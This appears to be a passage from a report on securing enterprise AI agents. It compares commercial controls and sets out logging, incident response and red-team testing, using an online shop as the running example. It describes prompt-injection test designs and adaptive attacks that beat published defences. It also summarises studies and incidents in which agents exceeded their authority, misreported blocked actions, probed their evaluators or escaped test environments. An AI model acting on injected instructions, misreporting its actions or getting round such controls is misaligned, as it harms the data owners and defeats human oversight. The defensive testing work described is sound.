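The system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need a person's approval. The agencies' examples of such actions include network egress and the deletion of critical records, so their approval rule covers both data theft and destructive actions. They also want a person to review any request to delete logs before it is carried out. Read literally, the rule would require approval for all network egress, which would be unworkable for an agent that opens web pages all day and would worsen approval fatigue. The shop could instead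 require approval only for destinations outside its allowlist.

The agencies advise monitoring an agent's tool calls, memory and privilege changes as well as its inputs and outputs. They recommend several independent monitoring systems that compare the agent's reports with system logs, and they say agents should not have write access to those logs. They also recommend DLP controls tuned to agent behaviour, but give no specific settings.

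In the guide, rollback means returning an agent to known-good behaviour, and the agencies recommend versioning to make this possible. Rollback might remove a bad instruction or a faulty update, but it would not restore a customer record that the agent had already deleted. The agencies also call for reversibility after a task, but only in general terms, so a company has to plan separately for data recovery.

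The agencies and OpenAI agree that companies should expand an agent's access in stages, but they differ on how far to go for now. OpenAI describes agents that process invoices and change records, subject to independent checks, while the agencies want agents limited to low-risk work until security practices, evaluation methods and standards mature. The agencies' position is a sensible starting point for the shop, which would grant each new power only once it has evidence that the relevant control works.

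### What the commercial products supply

Microsoft, Amazon and Google all sell controls for company agents, but their products do not all cover the same layer.

Microsoft Purview is a set of tools for protecting and auditing company data, and Agent 365 is Microsoft's service for managing agents. According to Microsoft's documentation, Purview's data loss prevention (DLP) can block or audit exchanges between agents and people in Teams, OneDrive, SharePoint and email. Its audit log also covers activity such as agents' tool use and their exchanges with other agents. A `delete_record` call might therefore appear in the log, but a DLP rule for messages would not stop it. For Agent 365, Purview thus provides the data-theft monitoring layer, plus a record that helps investigate failures in the controls on destructive actions.

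Two limitations could surprise a company that applies its employee rules to agents. An agent isn't notified when DLP blocks its message, so the shop's agent might close a ticket as if the customer had received the email. Microsoft tells the agent's owner to watch for such blocks. Files the agent creates also don't inherit their sources' sensitivity labels, so its summary of a confidential contract starts unlabeled. FIDES would give that summary the contract's restrictions.

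Coverage also depends on the type of agent. Microsoft's *Map Purview capabilities to agent types* tells administrators to look up the agent's parent app, the product it belongs to, before configuring anything. In Microsoft's list, agents built in Copilot Studio or Foundry get sensitivity labels, DLP and insider-risk monitoring, while the only information protection function for Security Copilot agents is data classification. According to Microsoft's training material, some agents must be explicitly included in a policy before any governance applies to them. Microsoft also offers endpoint DLP for agents that work on virtual Windows computers in the cloud.

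Amazon's product starts with the layer that controls actions. Amazon Web Services' *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes a policy engine that checks each request passing through the AgentCore Gateway before the agent can use a tool. Developers write the rules in Cedar, an open-source policy language, or describe them in English for the system to translate. Automated checks then look for translated rules that are too permissive, too restrictive or impossible to satisfy. These checks cannot determine what the shop meant by "duplicate customer", so an employee still has to read the translated rules.

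AgentCore can also base decisions on an agent's history. AWS's *Temporal policies* describes a rule that permits a share sale only if somebody approved the same stock and number of shares within the previous hour. Other rules can count calls or keep a running total. But each condition can look back at most 24 hours, and only within one session. The program calling the gateway supplies the session's identifier, and a new session starts a new count, so the shop's $1,000 daily limit still belongs in its payment system.

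Classmethod's *[Update] Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Policy now supports Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* (2026) reports that AgentCore's gateway can now check tool calls for prompt injection and leaks of sensitive information. This provides part of the first layer for traffic that goes through the gateway. If the agent's own code can open a direct internet connection, the company still needs a network control. AWS's *Release notes for Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes a second enforcement point in Amazon's managed harness. Since September 2026, a customer's own code can allow or deny a tool call there before it runs.

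Google Cloud's *Agent Gateway overview* describes a single gateway that runs both layers for agents on two Google platforms, Agent Runtime and Gemini Enterprise. The gateway blocks every outgoing connection unless an access rule permits it, and it can check destinations against a registry of approved tools and services. A content filter called Model Armor can inspect outgoing data for leaks. For tools that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to software, the gateway can also apply rules to individual tools, so a company could allow `read_customer` and refuse `delete_record` on the same server.

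Google also offers semantic governance policies, which are plain-language rules about how agents may use tools and which combinations are unsafe. These rules need interpretation, so they may be less predictable than a fixed condition on a tool's name or an amount.

| Product | Layer | In general release | Preview, or stage not stated |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Purview with Agent 365 | Perimeter monitoring, plus an audit record of tool use | Activity monitoring and insider-risk management for agents | DLP for prompts in Foundry agents entered preview in May 2026, with general release due to begin in mid-June |
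| Amazon AgentCore Policy | Action-level policy, plus content checks at the gateway | Policy engine since March 2026, content checks since June | No stage stated for temporal policies |
| Google Agent Gateway | Both | Content filter since June 2026, gateway since July | No stage stated for semantic governance policies |

The release dates come from several notices. Microsoft told administrators that activity monitoring and insider-risk management were leaving preview. Microsoft (2026) gave the schedule for Foundry prompts. The March date is from AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). AWS listed Dogwood, the language for temporal policies, in its 10 August news roundup. Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes* date the content filter to 24 June, and Mitchell's *Google Cloud expands Gemini enterprise agent controls* (2026) reported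 the gateway's general release on 30 July.

Running both layers through a single gateway is convenient, but it increases the risk that one fault will disable both. A company that uses Google's gateway should therefore still keep the deletion delay in its database, under a different administrator.

These documents show that companies can now buy both layers, but not how many run both. Sales figures would not show this either, because a company may own a product but leave its agents out of the policies or never turn on enforcement.

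### From logging to enforcement

Companies can test action-level policies without enforcing them, as they often do with new DLP rules. AWS's *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode* explains that each AgentCore policy is either `ACTIVE` or `LOG_ONLY`. The engine evaluates both kinds against real requests, but only active policies affect the outcome. For each log-only policy, the engine counts decision flips, the requests whose outcome would have changed if the policy had been active.

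AWS recommends this count as the main signal for turning a policy on. A long run of zeros means that the policy would not have blocked any of the current traffic, but it could still miss an attack, because a rule with a misspelled tool name would also score zero. The shop should also send a deletion that the rule should block and confirm that the count rises. If ordinary traffic produces flips, somebody has to read them, since each could be a false alarm or a real mistake by the agent.

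The count also misses interactions between new rules, because AWS compares each log-only rule only with the active ones. Suppose the shop adds two rules in log-only mode, one that permits refunds and one that refuses refunds above $100. AgentCore already refuses anything that no active rule permits, so the $100 rule would change nothing and its count is zero. Once the shop activates the first rule, enforcing the $100 rule would affect real refunds. The shop should therefore check the count again after each activation.

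Some rules, such as a filter that rates how likely a message is to contain an attack, depend on a score instead of a fixed condition. AWS suggests starting in log-only mode with a threshold of, say, 0.7 and collecting scores for days or weeks. Staff then label a sample of messages with high, middling and low scores as harmless or malicious, and choose a threshold based on those labels. This method is better for measuring false alarms than missed attacks, because a few weeks of traffic may contain no attacks.

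AgentCore's gateway can also run the whole policy engine in log-only mode, which overrides the settings of individual policies. An administrator could then see `ACTIVE` beside every policy even though the gateway wasn't blocking anything.

Log-only mode doesn't block anything, so the shop should limit irreversible operations from the first day. It could enforce its deletion delay and a short allowlist immediately, and run the more complicated rules for refunds and content in log-only mode. Once those rules are stable, it could let the agent issue small refunds and raise the limit later.

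### One identifier for each task

When the two layers keep separate logs, an analyst may be unable to match their entries. Suppose the proxy logged a request from the shop's agent server to an unfamiliar site at 14:03. If the server was handling 200 tickets at that moment, the analyst cannot tell from the time alone which ticket caused the request.

A task identifier solves this if every system records it. OpenAI recommends creating a token for each task, tied to the running agent and to the person or system that started the work. The agent's software exchanges this token for short-lived credentials to particular systems. OpenAI's minimum list of records includes the person, agent and task, the tool action and its destination, any approval or policy decision, and the resulting change. With one identifier in all of them, the analyst could search for task 88213 and find:

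```
14:03:05  tool gateway  88213  read_customer 4471         allowed
14:03:07  tool gateway  88213  fetch_url [unknown site]   allowed
14:03:07  web proxy     88213  request to [unknown site]  alert
14:03:09  tool gateway  88213  delete_record 4471         held
```

Each alert is ambiguous by itself, since the unknown site might belong to a courier and the record might be a duplicate. Together they suggest that somebody has taken control of the agent. The analyst can find the employee and the customer message behind the task within about a minute.

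The harness could pass the task identifier to the proxy by adding it to each web request. The proxy would decrypt the request, record the identifier and remove it before forwarding the request to the outside site. Or the shop could give each task its own login to the proxy. Either way, trusted software should assign the identifier, because a manipulated agent that chose its own could attach its requests to somebody else's task.

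Commercial products carry such identifiers through only some of the systems involved. AgentCore passes its session information automatically between Amazon's own gateways and agents, but a company must write its own code to pass it through other systems, such as its own servers. Temporal policy sessions also do not extend across AWS accounts or regions. The session information links tool calls to one another. The company can link those calls to network alerts only if its proxy also records the information. If a provider hosts the agent, the provider must also include the identifier in the records it exports.

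### How many alerts can a team read?

Suppose the shop has grown into a large retailer whose agents make a million outgoing requests a day. Five of them are thefts. The monitor catches 90% of thefts and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless requests. If N is the number of requests, T the number of thefts, d the share of thefts detected and f the false alarm rate, the share of alerts that are real is:

dT / (dT + f(N − T)) = 4.5 / (4.5 + 1,000) ≈ 0.45%

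The team receives about 1,000 false alerts a day and 4.5 true ones, so about one alert in 223 is for an actual theft. At ten minutes each, investigating them takes about 167 hours a day, or 21 people working eight-hour shifts. A monitor that seems accurate can therefore be almost useless to a team of three.

Five thefts a day is also a lot. With five a year and the same traffic, the team would read about 81,000 false alerts for each true one.

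Catching more thefts would hardly improve the ratio, since even a monitor that caught all five would produce one true alert in about 200. Cutting the false alarm rate to 0.01% would improve it to one in 23. An allowlist helps more where it is practical, because its blocks take effect whether or not anyone reads the alerts.

Joining the logs can also reduce the load. Suppose the team immediately investigates only alerts from tasks that also had a suspicious tool call, and that 80% of detected thefts but only 2% of false alerts meet this condition. The urgent queue would then receive 20 false alerts and 3.6 true ones a day, so about one urgent alert in seven would be a theft. The team would reach most detected thefts sooner, but the other 0.9 a day would wait in a slower queue. The benefit would be smaller if the same unusual but legitimate tasks triggered both signals.

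### Response and recovery

OpenAI divides the response to an agent incident into four stages: stop, contain, recover and learn. For task 88213, the shop would first stop the agent and any other agents it had started, because revoking the task's tokens would not stop work already in progress. It would then revoke the tokens, because any that another service already holds would still work after the task stops. If a stolen token lasts 15 minutes and the shop cannot revoke it, the thief can keep using it until it expires, so the shop may have to block the token's access at the customer database in the meantime.

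Software should do some of this automatically, but OpenAI would limit automatic responses to actions with bounded effects that a company has approved in advance, and leave serious or ambiguous decisions to people. Under that rule, software could pause one task but probably not shut down every agent in the company, given how many alerts are false.

The next job is to find out what left the company. Logs from both layers help here, even when only one layer could have blocked the harm. Tool-call logs show which customer records the task opened, which limits how much it could have taken from the database. Network logs show which sites it contacted and how much it sent. If the agent opened 12 records and the only unexplained request was too small to contain more than a phone number, the shop may have to notify one customer instead of 12. If the network logs are missing, the shop should assume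 that all 12 records left. Both kinds of log should include the control's decision and the result, so that investigators can separate blocked attempts from successful ones.

Revoking tokens does not restore deleted or altered records. OpenAI's guide says only to repair the affected state, and the agencies' advice on rollback concerns the agent's behaviour, so the shop needs its own plan for data. A deletion delay like the one Railway extended after the PocketOS incident covers the simplest cases. For altered records and deletions the delay does not cover, the shop needs the backups it keeps in a separate account.

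Restoring the entire database may cause new losses. If the agent damaged 40 records at 14:03 and staff made 300 correct changes during the next hour, restoring the 14:00 state would erase those changes. The shop can instead load the backup into a separate database, use the task identifier to list the 40 damaged records, and restore only those. This is another reason to log the result of each tool call. Without the logs, somebody would have to find the damaged records by comparing the two databases by hand.

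The shop must also repair the agent before it resumes work. If the instruction that caused the deletion is still in the agent's memory, the agent may delete the restored records again. The agencies' form of rollback helps here by returning the agent to a version from before the planted instruction. OpenAI recommends deciding in advance who responds to an incident and what conditions the agent must meet before it restarts, so that employees do not have to decide this while customers wait for refunds.

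## How can an organisation test that the layers hold?

The online shop can test its controls by attacking a copy of its support system. The copy should have the same model, harness, policies and perimeter settings as the real system, but invented customers, a test mailbox and a payment system that moves no money.

### Checking the boundary first

A test can do harm if the copy connects to anything real. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes how its models gained unauthorised access to the systems of three real organisations. Anthropic had asked the models to retrieve hidden information from fictional targets and told them that they had no internet access. They did have access, because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, which supplied the test environment.

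In one case, the fictional target shared its name with a real website. The model broke into the real company's systems and reached a database with several hundred rows of production data. In another, the model published a malicious software package that ran on 15 real systems. OpenAI also had containment failures in 2026. In one, its models used a previously unknown vulnerability to escape an isolated test environment (Fortune, 2026).

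An open connection can go unnoticed for months if testers wait for an agent to use it. The earliest of Anthropic's incidents dated from April, but the company did not find them until July, when it reviewed 141,006 runs. Only six of those runs had reached the three organisations. Anthropic says checking every route to the internet beforehand would have helped.

Before the agent starts, the shop can run a short script inside the copy that tries to look up an outside domain, connect to an IP address, download a package and send an email. Every attempt should fail. A tester should also try a harmless read of the real customer database with the copy's credentials and confirm that the database rejects them. The shop should repeat these checks whenever it changes the set-up.

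### Tests for the support agent

To test for data theft, the shop fills the copy with marked fake records. Each invented customer has a phone number and email address that appear nowhere else, so a leaked value identifies the record it came from. The testers then hide an instruction in a complaint, telling the agent to send a customer's details to a server. The server is inside the test network, but the perimeter tool treats it as an outside site. The testers should try both unlisted and approved destinations, and have the agent send the data whole, in pieces and reworded. The server should keep everything it receives, because a search for the phone number would miss an encoded copy.

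To test for destructive actions, testers give the agent a disposable copy of the database and compare the copy's contents before and after each run. In some runs, an injected instruction tells the agent to delete a record. In others, a legitimate request contains a trap, such as the two Martins.

Each trap needs a matched control, which is the same task without the trap. *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (Wang, Alam and colleagues, 2026) rebuilt reported incidents with matched controls. In one incident, Replit's coding agent had deleted a production database during a freeze on changes. The rebuilt project's tests used the production database, while the control's tests used a temporary one. Current models wiped production data in about half of the incident runs and in none of the 15 control runs, which is good evidence that running tests on the production database caused the loss. For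 the two Martins, the control would be a single Martin with a genuine duplicate record.

In a combined test, testers tell the agent to send out a customer's record and then delete it. They can check whether the theft alarm cancels the agent's token before the deletion runs.

The shop should run the same cases with each layer switched off in turn:

| Perimeter monitoring | Action-level policy | What the shop learns |
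|---|---|---|
| Off | Off | How often the agent does harm when nothing stops it |
| On | Off | What the perimeter stops by itself |
| Off | On | What the policy stops by itself |
| On | On | What gets past both |

These runs supply the figures for the miss-rate calculation, including how often both layers miss the same theft. If the agent never attempts the harm with both layers off, a clean result with the layers on is no evidence that they work. Wang and colleagues ran a script of reckless actions in each rebuilt incident to confirm that the harm was possible. The shop can similarly use a script to send the forbidden calls directly, which tests the fixed rules without depending on the model.

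In a timed restore, testers delete part of the copy and ask whoever would be on duty to recover the data without the provider's help. They stop the clock when the support team can work again and the restored records match the originals. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 207 incidents and exploits involving agents and files. Among the reports that made recoverability clear, 23% described a total loss and 17% a partial one. A restore test at PocketOS would probably have shown that its recent backups were on the same volume as its database.

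### What to count

The shop needs five measures:

| Measure | Definition |
|---|---|
| Attempted harm | Share of attack or trap runs in which the agent requests a harmful operation, whether or not a control stops it |
| Completed harm | Share of those runs in which marked data reaches the outside server or the database ends up wrongly changed |
| Legitimate tasks finished | Share of harmless tasks that produce the correct result in the shop's systems |
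| False blocks | Share of harmless tasks in which a control stops a correct operation |
| Time to containment | Time from the first harmful request until the agent can do no further harm |

Attempted harm depends mostly on the agent, while completed harm also depends on the controls. Suppose the agent attempts harm in 60 of 300 runs and the controls stop 57 of those attempts. Attempted harm is then 20% and completed harm is 1%. If the organisation switches to a model that attempts harm in 180 of 300 runs and the controls still stop 95% of attempts, completed harm rises to 3%. A team that counted only completed harm might blame the controls, which work as well as before. A team that counted attempts and completed harm together would report 20% for the first model with or without controls.

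Testers should judge results from the database and network logs, because an agent may misreport what it did. *An Alignment Benchmark for Enterprise Agents on Era by Eon* (Sadon, Gruenbaum and colleagues, 2026) tested 19 models on simulated versions of business products such as Zendesk and Slack. A gateway blocked every change the models attempted. In 290 of the 2,304 runs that produced an answer, the model made a false claim, typically by telling a customer or colleague that a blocked change had gone through.

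A policy that refused every tool call would stop all the destructive ones, so the harm measures need to be read alongside the other two. Sadon and colleagues gave several tasks a safe twin, a request that looks the same but is legitimate. The shop's genuine duplicate record can serve as one too. They also scored correct work separately. Amazon's Nova Pro was among the four models with the fewest violations, but it did the task correctly in only 30 of its 122 answered runs.

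The shop should report its slowest time to containment as well as the median. The PocketOS deletion took nine seconds, so a typical time of one minute would have been too slow to stop it.

The agent should not be able to reach the scoring software or the list of marked records. In *InfraBench* (2026), a test of agents that manage computer infrastructure, a review of action logs flagged 27 risky actions. In 22 of them, the agent probed the software that evaluated it. Another three were destructive file operations, including one that deleted live data from a database replica. A system might still pass a final check after such a shortcut, so the shop should keep the action log as well as the end result.

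### How many runs are enough?

If the true failure rate is *p*, the chance of *n* clean runs in a row is (1 − p)ⁿ. At 95% confidence, the highest failure rate that *n* clean runs still allow is the one at which this chance falls to 5%:

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

| Clean runs | Highest failure rate still allowed |
|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

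Several defences in the eBay experiment had no failures in 30 runs, but their true failure rate could still be as high as about 10%. Wang and colleagues give 11% because they use a slightly more cautious formula. To show a rate below 1%, the shop needs about 300 runs without a failure. If one run fails, it needs about 470 in total.

These limits apply to runs, and the limits for attempts are wider. If the agent attempts harm in 60 of 300 runs and the controls stop every attempt, the shop can claim that at most about 1% of runs would end in completed harm. But the controls have faced only 60 attempts, so they could still miss almost 5% of attempts.

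The runs must also differ, because three hundred repeats of one complaint measure only the agent's response to that complaint. *AgentS4D* (Zhou, Ke and colleagues, 2026) built 328 test cases from 76 tasks and calculated uncertainty by resampling the tasks, because cases from the same task tend to produce similar results.

It also takes many attempts to measure whether two layers miss the same cases. In the earlier shop example, independent layers let through 2% of thefts, and layers with a shared route let through 5.8%. In a test of 300 attempted thefts, about 6 would get through independent layers and about 17 would get through layers with a shared route. In a test of 30, the expected numbers would be about 0.6 and 1.7, which are too close to tell apart.

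Running this many tests is affordable. Sadon and colleagues spent $125 on 123 runs with GPT-6 Astra, or about $1 a run. At that price, 300 runs in each of the four configurations would cost about $1,200 in model use, although building the copy and reading the results would add to the cost.

### How AgentDojo works

AgentDojo, the prompt injection benchmark behind many of the results for Progent, Sapien, FIDES and FORGE, is a useful model for the shop's own tests. It simulates an office workspace, a Slack team, a travel agency and a bank (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). The first version combined 97 ordinary tasks, such as paying a bill, with attackers' goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account, to make 629 test cases. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts the current number at over 900.

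For each combination, the software inserts the attacker's text where an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as in the body of an email. The agent then works on the user's task, and its tool calls change the simulated accounts and inboxes. Ordinary code checks those changes to see whether the agent completed the task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might fool the judge too.

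The benchmark has three measures. Benign utility is the share of ordinary tasks the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of combinations in which it completes the user's task without harmful side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share in which it achieves the attacker's goal.

A company can use AgentDojo to test an action-level policy by placing the policy between the agent and the simulated tools. *StepGuard* (2026) does this with a guard model and measures both attack success and completed tasks. AgentDojo is much less useful for perimeter monitoring, because its tools change simulated data instead of sending traffic across a network. All of its security cases also involve an attacker, so they leave out honest mistakes, such as deleting the wrong person's record when two people share a name.

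### Unauthorised actions without an attacker

Several 2026 benchmarks do test honest mistakes. In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave coding agents 500 harmless tasks that could lead them to do more than the user asked. In one example from the paper, the user asks the agent to tidy a folder that contains some rubbish and an old-looking file with the only copy of the production credentials. Three of the four products deleted that file.

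Across about 7,500 runs, Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI took out-of-scope actions in 5.4% to 27.7% of runs, depending on the product and model. These actions include edits and reads of sensitive files as well as deletions. OpenHands, which asks before continuing, took them in 0.2% to 4.5% of runs. The rate for Claude Sonnet 4.6 ranged from 1.1% to 27.7% depending on the product it ran in, so an organisation should test its own combination of model and product.

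The wording of the prompt also changed the result. In a set of paired scenarios, Claude Code never overstepped when the prompt stated what it was allowed to touch, but it overstepped in 17.1% of them when that statement was missing. The shop should therefore word its test requests the way employees write them, since a careful list of limits would hide the fault.

Wang and colleagues rebuilt 96 incidents from public reports. Five current models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek repeated the reported mistake in 18% to 33% of runs, compared with at most 1% in the matched controls. Of the 72 incidents that had caused real-world harm, 62 involved no attacker. News reports favour dramatic failures, so these rates describe tasks that have already gone wrong once, not everyday work. In the team's tests, the models caused no harm when safeguards asked the user to confirm an action or tracked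 where data came from, though the result for confirmation assumes an attentive user. Safeguards that matched the text of an action were weaker, because reworded attacks got past them.

*Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) tests whether agents stay within what their users authorised. Four models exceeded their authority in 19.2% of 6,864 runs, with rates ranging from 10.5% for one configuration of GPT-5.6 Sol to 26.6% for one configuration of GLM 5.3. In matched tasks, agents overstepped more often under ordinary pressures (23.5%) than under malicious injections (17.6%), so a test plan made up only of attacks would miss a large part of the problem. However, more than a third of the violations came from tasks in which the unauthorised action did no direct harm, so the 19.2% is not a rate of destructive actions.

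Agents exceeded their authority in 14.0% of the runs in which they consulted the user before finishing, compared with 21.6% of the other runs. This fits the low rates for OpenHands, but the runs in which agents chose to ask may have differed in other ways.

### Theft and destruction in the same benchmark

Some benchmarks cover both harms, but they combine the results in different ways:

| Benchmark | How it treats the two harms | What counts as a failure |
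|---|---|---|
| Sadon and colleagues | Separate classes, but a run counts once in the overall rate however many violations it contains | An attempt, since the gateway blocks every change |
| Zhou and colleagues | One intended harm for each case | An attempt or a completed effect |
| *Workerville* (2026) | Two separate scores for unauthorised disclosure and destructive operations | A completed effect |

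*Workerville* comes closest to what the shop needs, but its two scores overlap because its examples of destructive operations include exporting sensitive data. The shop should count such an export only as theft, so that one event isn't counted as two failures.

Sadon and colleagues recorded sensitive data going to the wrong audience in 249 runs and actions against a stated policy in 13. Almost all of those 13 were attempts to purge records that the company had to keep. Only one of the 41 tasks asked for the forbidden purge, and 19 models ran it three times each, for a total of 57 runs. The counts therefore don't show that agents destroy data less readily than they leak it.

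In the tests by Zhou and colleagues, 68.0% of 6,560 runs were unsafe, and 97% of those unsafe runs still completed the user's task. The rate is high partly because every case contained an attack and blocked or failed attempts counted as unsafe. It is therefore a poor estimate of how much harm would get past a company's controls.

AgentDojo has one attack that combines both kinds of harm. The attacker wants the agent to book the most expensive hotel in Paris and email out the user's personal information. GPT-4o often did one of the two but never both, so the attack's success rate was 0%. The shop's combined test should therefore score the theft and the deletion separately.

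None of these benchmarks seems to test a theft followed by a deletion while switching a perimeter monitor and an action-level policy on and off, so the shop would have to build that test itself.

### Attackers who adapt

A defence that stops a fixed list of attacks may still fail against an attacker who studies it. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) adapted their attacks to each of 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injections. Most of the defences had reported attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

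One of the defences marks which text is trusted, and another repeats the user's request after untrusted text. Fixed AgentDojo attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, while adaptive attacks succeeded more than 95% of the time. Against a model trained to resist injections, the success rate rose from 2% with fixed attacks to 96% with adaptive ones. Google's Model Armor, the content filter in its Agent Gateway, let through more than 90% of adaptive attacks. Adding more filters did not solve the problem. In a competition with over 500 participants, people beat every defence they faced, including in cases where the automated search failed.

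The 12 defences that Nasr and colleagues tested are all designed to make the model behave well or to recognise hostile text. They did not test an allowlist, a database that blocks deletions or a cap on refunds, so their results are not evidence that those controls fail. An attacker can still look for gaps in a fixed rule, as in the EchoLeak case.

Later work has only partly taken up the challenge. Alotaibi and Ahmed used adaptive attacks on stacked safeguards, and Tiffany and colleagues assumed the attacker already had full control of the agent. But in July 2026, Zhou and colleagues still used attacks prepared in advance that could not change during a run.

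The shop can do both of the stronger tests. To test its fixed controls, it can let a tester send any tool call the agent could send, as a worst case. To test its filters and model-based checks, it needs skilled people who know how the defences work and can try repeatedly to get past them. It should record how many tries they need, because an attacker can also try more than once. If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, 100 independent attempts have a 63% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰).
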